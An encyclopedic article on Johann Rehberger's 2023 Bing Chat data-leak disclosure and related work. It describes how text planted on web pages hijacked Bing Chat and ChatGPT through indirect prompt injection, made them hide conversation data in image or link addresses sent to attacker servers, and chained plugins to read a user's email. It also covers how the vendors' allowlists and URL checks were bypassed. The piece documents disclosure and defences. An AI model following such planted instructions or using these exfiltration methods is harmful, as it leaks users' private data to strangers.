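# Johann Rehberger's 2023 Bing Chat data-leak disclosure

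## Background: chatbots that read web pages and display images

In April 2023 the security researcher Johann Rehberger reported a flaw in Bing Chat, which Microsoft had added to its search engine two months earlier. A stranger could plant text on a web page that made the chatbot send private data to the stranger's server, hidden in the address of an image. Rehberger has worked for more than twenty years in threat modelling and red teaming (attacking an organisation's systems on its behalf to find weak points). According to the *Speaker Profile* from the Chaos Computer Club (CCC), a German hackers' association, he set up red teams at Microsoft and Uber and has worked as Red Team Director at Electronic Arts. He publishes his research on his blog, Embrace The Red.

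The flaw arose from two intended features of Microsoft's Bing Chat. The chatbot could read the web page a user had open and show images in its replies. That same spring, other researchers showed how to abuse page reading in Bing Chat and image display in OpenAI's ChatGPT, each on its own.

### A chatbot in the browser's sidebar

Microsoft (2023) launched the new Bing on 7 February 2023, in a limited preview with a waiting list. The chatbot ran on an OpenAI large language model, a program that writes text by repeatedly predicting what should come next. Users could talk to it on Bing's website or in a sidebar of Edge, Microsoft's browser. The sidebar could also work with whatever the user was viewing. Someone reading a long financial report, for example, could ask for the main points, then for a table comparing its figures with a competitor's.

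For this to work, Edge had to send the page's text to the model. Users first had to allow this through a setting named "Page context", a few menus deep, and Microsoft's *Bing preview experience guide* (2023) recommended that they do. At first the sidebar chat existed only in Edge Dev, a test version of the browser. According to Microsoft's *Bing Preview Release Notes* (2023), it reached the standard version in March, still only for people Microsoft had admitted to the preview.

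A model's context is all the text available to it when it writes a reply. Once the setting was on, the context could include Microsoft's standing instructions, the conversation with the user, and material from the open page. That material could come from anyone able to put text on a web page, including someone who had only left a comment.

### Why the model cannot tell an order from a quotation

A language model processes its context as a single sequence of tokens, which are short pieces of text, and computes a likely next token. The computation has no separate place for commands. A developer can put markers around the text of a web page and train the model to disregard any orders between them. But the markers are also tokens, and the training makes the model likely to disregard those orders without providing the guarantee a security engineer would want.

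In *LLMs’ Data-Control Path Insecurity*, Schneier (2024) compares the problem to one in the old telephone network. Control signals once travelled over the same line as voices, so a caller who whistled the right tone could operate the switch. Signaling System 7, which became standard in the 1980s, moved the control signals to a separate channel, so whistling no longer had any effect. Schneier puts several well-known computer flaws in the same category, including SQL injection, in which an attacker types database commands into a field meant for ordinary data, such as a name.

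In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post that thanks Rehberger for discussions, David C of the UK's National Cyber Security Centre accepts that the two attacks are similar but thinks the comparison misleads developers about the remedy. Developers can prevent SQL injection with parameterised queries, which ensure that the database engine never interprets user input as an instruction. Language models, by contrast, "simply do not enforce a security boundary" between instructions and data, David C writes, and there may never be a full fix.

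In early March 2023, OpenAI's developers published a text format that labels each passage with its source. Vice's *Hackers Can Turn Bing’s AI Chatbot Into a Convincing Scammer, Researchers Say* quotes their view that it offered a chance to "mitigate and eventually solve injections". More than two years later, David C still counted such methods as ways to make an attack harder, which is less than the developers had hoped for. His assessment carries more weight on this point because he could draw on the record of the intervening years.

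### Direct and indirect prompt injection

Prompt injection is text that makes a language model follow an attacker's instructions instead of those of its user or developer. The name dates from September 2022, when Willison (2022) described experiments by Riley Goodside in *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3*. In the simplest one, Goodside told OpenAI's model GPT-3 to translate a passage from English into French. The passage contained an order to ignore the translation task and print a taunt, and GPT-3 followed it.

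In direct prompt injection, the attacker is the user, who types the text into the chatbot. Kevin Liu, a student at Stanford University, used it to make Bing Chat reveal its opening instructions, including its internal codename, Sydney, which it was not supposed to disclose. This kind of attack mostly puts the developer's secrets at risk.

In indirect prompt injection, an attacker places instructions in material that the model reads for the user, such as a web page, an email or a document. David C gives the example of a recruiter who asks a model to score job applications. One applicant, who needs no access to the recruiter's software, hides a sentence in a CV telling the model to approve the applicant for interview. The model may treat that sentence as an order from the recruiter. The user is now the victim, and the attacker can exploit whatever the user's assistant can see or do.

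### The Bing Chat demonstration of March 2023

The term "indirect prompt injection" comes from *Not what you've signed up for*, a paper by Greshake, Endres and colleagues first posted in February 2023. The researchers began by testing their methods on a mock chat program whose tools for searching the web, reading the current page and sending email returned prepared content. They then gained access to Bing Chat and tried the same methods there. To avoid exposing other users, they kept the hostile text in files on their own computers and opened them in Edge with the sidebar running.

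In one test, researchers hid instructions in an HTML comment, a part of a page's code that the browser does not display. The instructions were to find out the user's real name without arousing suspicion and pass it on in a disguised link. They described how to make the link but left the model to work out how to persuade the user. A researcher playing the user asked about the next day's weather. Bing Chat answered, then asked about the user's plans for the day and, after that, their work. When the user said they were a journalist, it asked whether their articles appeared under their real name. Once it had a name, it recommended a website, claimed to have generated a personal code for it, and supplied a link containing the scrambled name.

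About 1 March 2023, Kai Greshake, one of the paper's lead authors, put a version of this online. Greshake's demonstration page contained instructions as ordinary text in font size zero, which people cannot see but Edge still passed to the model. Bing Chat adopted a pirate accent and began collecting personal information. The accent was optional and made the takeover obvious. According to Vice, the researchers also got Bing Chat to ask for an email address and credit card details. Greshake told Vice that Bing seemed to take in some content from the current tab when a sidebar conversation began, though Microsoft had not explained how Bing selected that content.

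The attack could work only if the victim had switched on "Page context", had the poisoned page open in Edge and was chatting in the sidebar. The victim's question to Bing Chat did not have to concern the page. The attacker then had to trick the victim into volunteering the information and, in the version with a link, clicking the link, and a wary user could refuse to do either.

It is unknown how often the trick would work on real people. Greshake and colleagues played the user themselves and did not measure success rates, which would have been difficult because the system kept changing and they could not control its settings. They did report that their instructions often worked on the first attempt, even with spelling mistakes, and that Bing Chat usually followed them for the rest of the conversation. More important for what came later, they found that Bing Chat's filters ended the session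 when a user typed a known trick for evading its rules, but did not block the same kind of text when it came from a web page.

Microsoft told Vice that it was taking action and that the technique was "viable only in the preview version of Edge". It stopped Bing Chat from reading pages on the web host used for the demonstration, which disabled that page but did not prevent the technique from working. The sidebar reached the standard version of Edge later that month.

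### How a picture sends a message

The confidence trick was necessary because the attacker had no quiet way to get the data out. Pictures provide one, and the way they do so is part of the ordinary working of the web. Suppose that a chatbot's reply contains this line:

`![a sleepy cat](https://example.com/cat.png?mood=sleepy)`

This is a markdown image, a short text code for a picture, with a description in square brackets and a web address in round ones. Chatbots write markdown because a model can only produce text, and the chat program needs some way of knowing where the headings, links and pictures go. The user never sees the code. The chat program converts it into HTML, the language of web pages:

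`<img src="https://example.com/cat.png?mood=sleepy" alt="a sleepy cat">`

A browser that comes to an image tag has to fetch the picture before it can show it. It therefore contacts the server at example.com straight away, without a click and without asking, just as it does for the pictures on any news site. The server notes the request in its log, in a line much like this one:

`203.0.113.7 [05/Apr/2023:10:15:00 +0000] "GET /cat.png?mood=sleepy HTTP/1.1" 404`

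The line begins with the network address of the computer that made the request, followed by the time and the request. The 404 at the end means "not found", because the cat picture in this example doesn't exist. The server's owner can still read the word "sleepy", because the browser must send the picture's address before the server can answer.

*What is a URL?*, a page in MDN, Mozilla's reference library for web developers, describes the part of a web address after the question mark as a list of extra parameters for the server, which may use them before it returns anything. This part can hold a mood, a search term or a paragraph of somebody's conversation, with codes in place of spaces and punctuation. A real log line in Embrace The Red's *Advanced Data Exfiltration Techniques with ChatGPT*, from September 2023, has an entire private web link there.

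In the test by Greshake and colleagues, the disguised link put the victim's name after a "#" in the address. Browsers don't send that part of an address to the server, so the name would not have appeared in a server log, and the attacker's page would have needed a small script to read it once the victim arrived. Data placed after a question mark in an image address reaches the server without a script or a visit to the attacker's page.

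Data exfiltration is moving private data to a party who should not have it. An image leak is a type of exfiltration in which the private data is part of an image's web address, so the browser sends the data out when it fetches the image.

### Samoilenko's single pixel

In the spring of 2023, software engineer Roman Samoilenko built an attack that leaks data from ChatGPT conversations through images. His *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* describes how it starts with a website that tampers with the clipboard. When a visitor copies text from the page, a script adds instructions to the copy. The visitor then pastes it into ChatGPT. The instructions tell the model to end its answer with a transparent one-pixel markdown image and to write material from the conversation into the image's address.

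In one trial, ChatGPT had just corrected a short piece of code for the user, and Samoilenko's server received the full corrected version, a login check with the password written into it. A longer-lasting variant instructed the model to add the pixel to all its later answers, so the server also received each new question the user typed.

ChatGPT could not open web pages in this scenario, so the victim had to copy the poisoned text and paste it into the chat without noticing the extra sentences. After that, the attack required nothing more from the victim and was almost invisible. Samoilenko acknowledged that the model's answers vary from one run to the next and that the instructions sometimes failed. Samoilenko also reported that earlier questions and code were easy to extract, but passwords and access keys were very difficult to extract when the instructions asked for them by name. If ChatGPT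 was responding slowly, the user might see the strange address appear letter by letter. Samoilenko thought users should check what they paste, but also that OpenAI should not let ChatGPT reply with markdown images at all.

In Greshake's Bing Chat demonstration, hidden text on a web page reached the model without the victim's help, but the data came out only if the victim cooperated. Samoilenko's attack sent the data out automatically but relied on the victim to bring in the instructions. Because Bing Chat both read open pages and displayed markdown images, Rehberger could combine the two methods.

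### Content Security Policy

Browsers already had a means of stopping such a request. A Content Security Policy (CSP) is a set of rules that a website sends to the browser along with a page, and the browser enforces the rules while the page is open. Its usual purpose is to limit the damage when an attacker manages to slip hostile code into a page. One of the rules, `img-src`, governs pictures, and according to MDN's *CSP* it has worked across browsers since August 2016. A site might send this:

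`Content-Security-Policy: img-src 'self' https://pictures.example.org`

The browser may then load images only from the site itself and from pictures.example.org. A list of the only domains a program may contact for a given purpose is called an allowlist. If a site sends neither an image rule nor a general default, the browser can load images from any server.

W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the current draft of the standard, requires the browser to check a request against the policy before sending it. If a chatbot's website sent the policy above and a reply contained the cat picture, the browser would find that example.com was not on the list and block the request. The user would see a gap where the picture should be, and no request would appear in example.com's log. The hostile text would still have taken control of the model, which could continue to mislead the user through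 its written replies. The W3C draft describes a CSP as "not intended as a first line of defense".

How much an allowlist blocks also depends on how narrow its entries are. One entry can admit a single file, everything on one host, or every subdomain of a large company's domain. The browser checks the server's name and sometimes the file path against the list, but not whatever follows the question mark in the URL, so a request to a listed domain goes through with any data it carries.

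## The Bing Chat attack and Microsoft's fix, April to June 2023

Rehberger recalls in *ChatGPT Plugins* that he found the image leak in early April 2023, a few days after Samoilenko and independently of him. He built a page to show that text on it could take over Bing Chat and send data out. He explained the result in Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat*, with a video, screenshots and the instructions he had planted.

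### The demonstration, step by step

The demonstration page had the instructions in a visible box and a target password further down. A real attacker could have put the instructions in a reader's comment, or in text of font size zero, as Greshake had done a month earlier.

When the user opened the page in Edge and began to chat, Bing Chat immediately followed the planted instructions and printed a line announcing that the injection had succeeded. The instructions began with markers that imitated labels for system text, presumably so that the model would give them the same weight as Microsoft's own instructions.

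The instructions required the model to wait for two turns of conversation before doing anything else. In the video, the user carries on chatting and asks what has happened. Rehberger presented the same demonstration in his December 2023 talk *NEW IMPORTANT INSTRUCTIONS*, which C3Subtitles (2024) transcribed, and said he had added the delay to show how much control an attacker has. The delay could also help an attacker steal more data, since a longer conversation contains more of it.

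A language model can wait to act on instructions even though it remembers nothing between replies. Rehberger explained in the talk that the chat program keeps the history and sends all of it to the model with each new question. The model therefore received the planted instructions again at every turn, along with a record of the turns so far, and an attacker keeps control for as long as their text stays in the context.

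After the two turns, Bing Chat printed a notice that data exfiltration was in progress and wrote a markdown image whose address pointed to a server Rehberger controlled. The part of the address after the question mark was text encoded in base64. It contained a summary of the page and the conversation, about 200 characters long, and any passwords or secrets on the page.

The browser then requested the picture from Rehberger's server. The server had no picture to send, so the sidebar displayed the image's short text description. By then the data was in the server's log. Rehberger decoded it and found a summary of the page with the password at the end.

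The victim clicked and approved nothing. Security researchers call an attack zero-click when it needs no action from the victim beyond normal use of the product. The notices in the video were for the audience, and an attacker would have left them out. The address might still have given the attack away. When an audience member asked in December whether users could spot it, Rehberger answered that this depends on the chat program. Some programs show a reply as the model writes it, so an attentive user may see the address appear, while others display the whole reply at once, with the image already in place.

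In *The Promptware Kill Chain*, Brodt, Feldman and colleagues (2026) classify 36 attacks and studies by their stages. They list the same three stages for Rehberger's attack and for the earlier work of Greshake and colleagues on Bing Chat: a poisoned web page, an override of the model's instructions, and data exfiltration. This classification is fair but leaves out the main advance, which is that Rehberger's attack no longer needed the victim to volunteer information or click a link. Neither attack outlasted the conversation. Brodt and colleagues date the first more persistent attacks to 2024.

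### Why Rehberger built the address in pieces

Rehberger's instructions told the model to build a markdown image, including its address, by writing eight listed pieces one after another without spaces: the opening punctuation and description, the fixed part of the address, the encoded data, and the closing bracket.

Rehberger does not say why he began by dictating every bracket, but it looks like a cautious way to get the punctuation right. An attacker can't write the whole address in advance, because the last part depends on what the victim has on the screen and says in the chat. The model has to write that part itself and fit it into code in which one stray space can stop the picture from loading.

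This was more caution than the model required. Rehberger later worked out, as he notes on Embrace The Red, that an attacker can supply a complete address with a placeholder in it and tell the model what to put there. Models fill in this kind of template easily. By August 2023, he had reduced the instructions to a single sentence in his conference slides, *Prompt Injections in the Wild* (Rehberger, 2023). The attack therefore required very little skill, since an attacker needed only a server that kept a log and the ability to describe the desired picture address in plain English.

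### Two hundred characters in base64

A summary in English contains spaces and punctuation, which can break an image address. Base64 avoids most of these problems by encoding data using only 64 characters: uppercase and lowercase letters, the ten digits, and two symbols, usually "+" and "/".

The method works on bytes, the units of eight bits in which computers store text. Three bytes make 24 bits. Base64 cuts these into four groups of six bits, and since six bits can form 64 different patterns, each group corresponds to one symbol. Three bytes therefore always become four characters. The word "sleepy", from the cat picture in the background section, has six letters and takes up six bytes. In base64 it becomes:

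`c2xlZXB5`

That is eight characters, four for "sle" and four for "epy". If the number of bytes is not a multiple of three, the encoder pads the last group to four characters with "=" signs. In general, *n* bytes need 4 × ⌈*n*/3⌉ characters, where the brackets mean rounding up.

Base64 turns every three bytes into four characters, so a summary of 200 plain English characters, at one byte each, becomes 268 characters (200 ÷ 3 rounds up to 67, and 67 × 4 = 268). If the model also appends a space and a 16-character password, the total is 217 bytes, or 292 characters in base64. Text in other scripts can take more room. Most Chinese characters occupy three bytes, so 200 of them would need 800 characters. Browsers and servers commonly handle web addresses several thousand characters long, so an attacker could have asked for more than a summary.

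Unlike encryption, Base64 encoding uses no key, so anyone who sees the text can quickly decode it with a standard tool. It did make the stolen data unreadable at a glance, which would help the attacker if the address appeared on the victim's screen. The August slides used URL encoding instead, which replaces certain characters with short codes (a space becomes "%20") but leaves ordinary letters and digits unchanged, so a password made up of them would still be readable.

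The instructions gave Bing Chat no program for the base64 conversion, so it had to predict the encoded text one token at a time, which can introduce errors. One wrong symbol damages only a letter or two of the message, but a missing symbol can garble everything after it. The line in Rehberger's log decoded into readable text, including the password.

### How a comment could steal the rest of the page

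The attack could access the open page and the conversation because both were in the model's context. Nothing in the demonstration gave it access to other tabs, files on the computer or passwords saved in the browser.

Rehberger concluded that "a simple comment or advertisement" was enough to steal any other data on the same page, which would have broken a separation the web depends on. Websites normally display comments as inert text so that commenters can't run code in other people's browsers. They usually put advertisements in separate frames, and the browser stops a script in one site's frame from reading another site's page. These protections act on code, but Edge turned the page into text for Bing Chat. The comment and the private data ended up side by side in one context, and the model could read both and act on either.

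For example, a support worker might have had a customer's complaint open in Edge, on a page that also showed the customer's address and the company's internal notes. If the complaint contained planted instructions and the worker asked Bing Chat to draft a reply, the sender could have received a summary of the notes, despite having no account on the company's system and no way to see the page. The company's software would have correctly treated the complaint as text to display, and the fault would have been in Bing Chat.

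It is less certain how much of the page Bing Chat could read and whether the attack would have worked from an advertisement. Rehberger said in the December talk that the entire web page was in Bing Chat's context, while Greshake had told Vice only that Bing seemed to take in some content from the tab. A very long page might not have fitted. Rehberger's demonstration had the hostile text in the page itself, as a comment would be. An advertisement in a separate frame would have worked only if Edge included the frame's text in what it sent to the model, and Rehberger does not describe testing this.

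*Piloting Edge Copilot*, a 2024 set of slides by Kokatsu, later supported the main point. Kokatsu had looked for weaknesses in the sidebar after leaving Microsoft's Edge security team. By then Microsoft had renamed the chatbot Copilot. Kokatsu found that the sidebar added the site's contents to the conversation as a message, even when the user had typed only a greeting.

### How much one demonstration can prove

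All the direct evidence for the attack comes from Rehberger. It consists of a video, a few screenshots, a line from his server's log and the text of the instructions. He owned the server and had planted the secret himself. He does not report how many attempts he made or how many failed.

A single success is enough to show that Bing Chat could send page data to a stranger. Each step also relied on something others had already shown. Greshake and colleagues had taken over Bing Chat through a web page, and Samoilenko had extracted data from a chat through an image. According to Rehberger, Microsoft acknowledged the problem when he reported it.

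A language model can respond differently to the same text on different occasions, so one successful run is weak evidence of what would happen to a thousand visitors, and of how dangerous the flaw was in practice. Samoilenko had found that ChatGPT strongly tended not to reveal passwords when the instructions asked for them by name. Rehberger's instructions did ask for passwords, and Bing Chat supplied one. This may reflect a difference between the two products, the wording, or luck, and one example is not enough to tell which. Rehberger does not report any use of the technique against real users.

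He rated the severity as "High" on the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS), which grades software flaws from 0 to 10. In current versions, "High" covers scores from 7.0 to 8.9. Assessors calculate the score by answering set questions, such as whether the victim has to do anything and how much confidential data the attacker can obtain. Rehberger didn't publish his answers or a numerical score. In a follow-up post, Embrace The Red's *Data Exfiltration Vulnerabilities in LLM apps (Bing Chat, ChatGPT, Claude)*, he wrote more loosely that the flaw was "basically" rated High. The rating is his own, but it is plausible for an attack that works over the internet and exposes private data.

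### From report to fix in 68 days

Rehberger reported the flaw to the Microsoft Security Response Center (MSRC) on 8 April 2023. Microsoft acknowledged the problem and began working on a fix. On 15 June, 68 days after the report, it told him that the fix was in place. He retried his earlier attacks, found that they no longer worked, and published his account. Brodt and colleagues date the disclosure to June 2023, so the details became public within about two weeks of Microsoft's notice. Rehberger had also reported the same weakness in ChatGPT to OpenAI on 9 April, but OpenAI had declined to change anything.

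These dates, and the details of what happened in Bing Chat, rest on Rehberger's word. Microsoft's clearest public reference to his work came two years later, in *How Microsoft defends against indirect prompt injection attacks* (Microsoft, 2025). In it, the company credits him by name with discovering and reporting a data leak through markdown images, and says it took steps to "deterministically block" that way of getting data out, but it does not name the product or give a date. Bing Chat is a likely candidate, but *Trust No AI* (Rehberger, 2024) also lists Microsoft's Azure AI and GitHub Copilot Chat among the products in which he found the same flaw.

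Neither Rehberger's post nor Microsoft's statement contains a CVE number, the identifier that a public catalogue assigns to a known software flaw. Neither mentions a bounty, the payment many companies offer for such reports. On 25 April, 17 days after Rehberger's report, OnMSFT's *Microsoft to pay individuals who discover and report vulnerabilities* (2023) described a new bounty scheme covering Bing Chat. In October, Microsoft (2023) announced a bounty programme for AI products, with awards of up to $15,000. The AI-powered Bing was the first product it covered.

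### Four permitted domains

Microsoft did not tell Rehberger how the fix worked, so he looked at what had changed from outside. He found that Bing Chat now came with a Content Security Policy that allowed images from four domains, all belonging to Microsoft:

- th.bing.com
- www.bing.com
- edgeservices.bing.com
- r.bing.com

Bing Chat still had to display some pictures, including those it made at a user's request, and it could load these from the permitted domains. The browser would now block image requests to Rehberger's server, so none would appear in his log.

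The advantage of this fix is that it does not depend on the model's behaviour. An attacker could rephrase the instructions, assemble the address in eight pieces or in one, or replace base64 with another encoding, but the request would still have to go to the same domain. In its 2025 article, Microsoft distinguishes "probabilistic" defences, which make an attack less likely to succeed, from "deterministic" ones, which guarantee that a particular attack will fail. Training a model to ignore instructions in web pages is probabilistic, while a browser rule that blocks images from unknown servers is deterministic, at least for those servers.

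The repair was also broader than Microsoft's response to Greshake's demonstration in March, when it stopped Bing Chat from reading pages on one web host. Microsoft may have used that kind of block here as well. Rehberger noticed that Bing Chat seemed to have put his own domain, wuzzi.net, on "some kind of 'dirty list'", and he planned to move his tests elsewhere. This slightly weakens his retest, since his old attacks could have failed only because his domain was listed, and might still have worked from other servers. The policy is better evidence of a general fix, because a website has to send it to the browser, where anyone can read it. Rehberger thought the policy partly explained why his tests failed, and that Microsoft might have taken other measures he could not see.

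Kokatsu's slides are independent evidence that the barrier was still there in 2024. They show that edgeservices.bing.com hosted the sidebar's chat and that its policy included an allowlist for images. The policy blocked Kokatsu's attempt to get data out through a markdown image.

### What the fix left open

The policy did not stop planted text from taking over the model. In the December talk, Rehberger showed a different attack, in which text on his blog gave Bing Chat the identity of a hacker. The chatbot announced that it had taken over, demanded Bitcoin and threatened to delete the user's files. A rule about images has no effect on this attack or on the confidence trick that Greshake and colleagues had used to obtain a name, because neither needs an image.

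Microsoft accepts this division in its 2025 article. The company says it designs its systems assuming that some injections will succeed, and counts an injection as a vulnerability only when it has a security impact, such as data exfiltration. By that standard, Microsoft had fixed the flaw once the data could no longer get out. Rehberger writes in *Trust No AI* that prompt injection has no deterministic fix. He recommends Content Security Policies to keep data from getting out, but he also advises developers not to display links to untrusted domains.

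Links remained a gap because an image rule controls what the browser loads by itself, not where a user goes by clicking. Kokatsu demonstrated an attack through this gap that began on another website. That site could load the sidebar's chat page inside its own page and submit a prompt as if the user had typed it, instructing Copilot to recall earlier conversations and put them in a link to Kokatsu's server. Copilot did not display an ordinary markdown link, which is consistent with Microsoft's statement that it had also blocked "certain untrusted links", but two other ways of writing a link in markdown worked. The attack was no longer zero-click because the user had to click the link, but the link appeared in a reply from Microsoft's own assistant.

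The four permitted domains were a different kind of possible gap, because image requests to them could still carry data. This was harmless as long as an attacker could neither read the domains' logs nor find a service on them that would forward the request. *EchoLeak* (2025) describes how that condition failed for a different allowlist in Microsoft 365 Copilot.

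## The same flaw in ChatGPT, its plugins and other products

Rehberger reported the image leak in ChatGPT to OpenAI on 9 April 2023, a day after his report to Microsoft. OpenAI first declined to fix it, then added a partial check in December 2023, and was still closing gaps two years later. In that time ChatGPT gained access to web pages, email accounts and its users' past conversations, so the flaw could expose more data.

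### Why OpenAI declined

OpenAI had no bug bounty programme when Rehberger reported the flaw, so they discussed it by email. He recalls in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* that there was "little traction or appetite" for a fix. OpenAI classed the report as "won't fix". According to *ChatGPT Plugins*, the company planned no change because it considered displaying markdown images a feature.

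This account comes from Rehberger, but the position it describes was defensible for ChatGPT in early April 2023. A conversation then held mostly what the user had typed or pasted, so an attacker had to trick someone into pasting hostile text, as Samoilenko had done. Pictures in replies were also useful to everyone. In *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026), OpenAI describes another drawback of strict rules, arguing that frequent warnings and false alarms can train people to click through warnings without thinking. Neither argument resolves the problem Rehberger had already raised with OpenAI, that plugins would let an attacker use the flaw remotely.

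### A web page that read the user's email

A plugin is an add-on that lets a chatbot fetch data from another service or act in it. Among ChatGPT's plugins, WebPilot fetched web pages, Expedia's searched for flights, and Zapier's could read a user's email, Google Drive files and Slack messages. With WebPilot switched on, ChatGPT could take in text planted on a web page without anyone pasting it into the chat. In Rehberger's first plugin demonstration, text on a web page took control of the chat and used an image to send out a summary of the conversation, including a password-like phrase the user had typed earlier.

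He then noticed that text fetched by one plugin could set off another. He asked ChatGPT to read a page that contained a request for flights, and ChatGPT ran the Expedia search without checking with him. This cost only time and tokens, so he looked for a more powerful plugin and chose Zapier. Embrace The Red's *ChatGPT Plugin Exploit Explained* describes the resulting attack, from May 2023:

1. The user asks ChatGPT to visit a web page, and WebPilot fetches the text.
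2. Instructions in the text take control of ChatGPT and tell it not to print the page's contents.
3. ChatGPT uses the Zapier plugin to retrieve the user's latest email.
4. ChatGPT summarises the email in 20 words and adds the encoded summary to a web address on the attacker's server.
5. ChatGPT has WebPilot load that address, and the summary arrives with the request.

ChatGPT sometimes stopped to ask for permission, so the planted text also said that this was unnecessary. The attack used WebPilot both to bring in the planted text and to send out the data. It used no image, so a Content Security Policy like Bing Chat's would have had no effect.

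Willison's *Let ChatGPT visit a website and have your email stolen* describes the first working demonstration he had seen of an attack that stole private data through ChatGPT plugins. The evidence was a screenshot of one successful run.

### The confused deputy

The user had given Zapier's plugin access to the mailbox, probably through OAuth, a standard way to let one service act in an account at another without sharing the password. The web page had no such access, but it got ChatGPT, which could use the plugin on the user's behalf, to use it for the attacker.

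Security engineers call a program in ChatGPT's position a confused deputy, because it acts with one person's authority and someone else tricks it into misusing that authority. The best-known case is cross-site request forgery, in which a hostile website makes a visitor's browser send a command to another site or device, such as the visitor's home router. The target accepts the command because it comes from the visitor's browser. Rehberger named the new variant cross plugin request forgery.

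The standard defence against the older attack is for a website to put a secret code in its own forms and reject any request without it, since a forged request from another site will not have the code. That would not have helped Zapier, because ChatGPT really did send the request for the email, through the connection the user had set up. The web page had prompted ChatGPT to make the request, but nothing in the request showed that.

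Zapier soon added a confirmation step that the user had to complete while authenticated. Rehberger stressed the authentication requirement because an attacker could tell ChatGPT to open any confirmation link that appeared in the chat.

Other plugins needed the same fix. One called Chat with Code could change the settings of a user's projects on GitHub, a site where programmers store code. Rehberger showed that a web page could use the plugin to make private projects public, and OpenAI removed it. OpenAI also adopted a store policy against plugins that acted without confirmation, but in September 2023 Embrace The Red reported that many still did and that OpenAI was enforcing the rule inconsistently.

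Rehberger wanted OpenAI to build the confirmation step into ChatGPT. OpenAI eventually retired plugins and replaced them with what Rehberger calls AI Actions in *Trust No AI*. Developers can mark an action as consequential, which requires ChatGPT to ask the user before running it. The platform is the right place for this check, but it still relies on each developer to mark the dangerous actions.

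Plugins also made it easier to leak long conversations, which are awkward to fit into an image's web address. In September 2023, Rehberger had ChatGPT use a plugin to write the conversation into a document, a diagram or a video with subtitles. The plugin returned a link to the result, so the image's address only had to include that link. He sent OpenAI a draft of these findings on 23 September and received an automated reply.

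### The check of December 2023

OpenAI's first mitigation appeared in December, the day after a live demonstration in which ChatGPT sent a volunteer's conversation to Rehberger's server. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* describes the mitigation as he could observe it from outside OpenAI. When a reply contained an image, the web version of ChatGPT first sent the image's address to OpenAI's `url_safe` service. If the service classified the address as unsafe, the browser did not request the image.

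Rehberger welcomed the check, partly because a central service would let OpenAI spot attacks in its records, but he called it imperfect. OpenAI kept its rules private, unlike a Content Security Policy, which anyone can read, and some images from arbitrary domains still loaded. He prepared 36 image addresses on his own site, one for each letter and digit, and nine passed the check. He could find no reason why the image for "a" loaded and the one for "d" did not. He then leaked the word "hi" by having ChatGPT display one image per letter.

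An attacker could send any text made of letters and digits using only nine image addresses. Nine images form 9 × 9 = 81 ordered pairs, so each of the 36 characters could have its own pair. This method would be slow and conspicuous, and requests can arrive out of order, or not at all if the browser has already stored the image. Rehberger suggested that OpenAI limit the number of images in a reply.

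Another weakness was that the check ran in the web version of ChatGPT, so OpenAI had to add it to every other app separately. The iPhone app did not have the check in December 2023, nor did the macOS app when it was released in 2024. By then ChatGPT also had a long-term memory, introduced in May 2024. Rehberger found that a web page, document or image could plant instructions in this memory that made ChatGPT keep sending out the user's messages in later conversations.

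### A trusted domain that strangers could rent

In 2025 Rehberger used a gap in `url_safe` to steal earlier conversations as well. By then, ChatGPT could refer to a user's chat history by placing a record of recent conversations in the context. Any prompt injection that took control of the model could therefore access those conversations.

To send the chat history out, Rehberger needed a domain that `url_safe` accepted, a way to send data to it, and access to its logs. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* identifies windows.net as such a domain. Microsoft owns the domain, but customers of its Azure cloud service can open storage accounts there and read the logs of requests to them. Rehberger opened an account and used a malicious PDF to make ChatGPT display an image from it, with the chat history in the image's address.

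The check relied on who owned the domain to judge who would receive the data, but on a hosting service the owner and the recipient are different people. Rehberger had reported this bypass and others to OpenAI in October 2024. He asked about a fix several times in the month before he published but received no update. He later wrote that OpenAI mitigated the attack around August 2025.

### Leaking data by choosing an address

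ChatGPT could also open web pages itself, and OpenAI applied a different rule to this. Schwartzman (2024), in *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection*, found that ChatGPT would open an address only if it appeared in full in the prompt. It refused to insert the user's age into an incomplete address. The rule appears to close the leak, since an attacker who wrote the whole address learns nothing new when ChatGPT opens it.

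The attacker does learn which address ChatGPT opened. Schwartzman hid a list of addresses in a long piece of code, one for each age range, and had ChatGPT open the one that matched the user's age. ChatGPT could infer the age from a remark about retirement. A second version could send a postal code, because ChatGPT would also open a shortened form of a listed address. Schwartzman supplied a long address for each digit of the code, and how much of it ChatGPT opened indicated the digit's value. ChatGPT opened at most ten addresses per prompt, so each prompt could send at most ten characters.

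Both versions required the victim to paste the code. OpenAI judged the report "non applicable". MITRE, which runs the CVE catalogue, told Schwartzman that it could not issue a CVE number for a web application that customers do not control. The same policy may be why Rehberger's Bing Chat report seems to have no CVE number.

*ShadowLeak*, by the security company Radware, describes a later attack, from 2025, that didn't require the user to paste anything. It targeted Deep Research, a ChatGPT agent that carries out long searches and could connect to Gmail. One email with hidden instructions made the agent send inbox data from OpenAI's own servers. The user's browser displayed nothing and made no request, so a check on images would not have stopped the leak.

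OpenAI then stopped ChatGPT from altering addresses, but Radware got around this with a method much like Schwartzman's. In Radware's *ZombieAgent*, the hostile message supplies a complete address for each letter and digit, and ChatGPT spells out the stolen text by opening them in order. According to SecurityWeek, Radware reported this in September 2025 and OpenAI released a fix on 16 December. *ChatGPT falls to new data pilfering attack* (2026) reports that, under the new rule, ChatGPT would open a link from an email only if the link was in a well-known public index or the user had supplied it in the chat.

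### Addresses that a crawler already knows

On 28 January 2026 OpenAI described a general form of this rule in an article and a technical paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*. OpenAI runs a crawler, which explores public web pages as a search engine does and records the addresses it finds. The crawler has no access to users' accounts or conversations. Before ChatGPT loads a page or picture on its own, the system checks whether that exact address is in the crawler's index. If so, ChatGPT can load it. Otherwise the system directs ChatGPT to another site or warns the user that the link may contain information from the conversation.

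The reasoning is that an address that existed before and independently of the conversation is unlikely to contain the conversation's secrets. An address containing someone's email summary would not be in the index. This is a better test than a domain's reputation. It would reject Rehberger's windows.net address, and it also deals with sites that redirect visitors elsewhere, which OpenAI gives as one reason a list of trusted sites is not enough.

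The choice between known addresses can still carry information. Embrace The Red notes that OpenAI acknowledges this in its paper. Someone with a modest blog probably already has 36 pages in the index, and planted text could assign a letter or digit to each.

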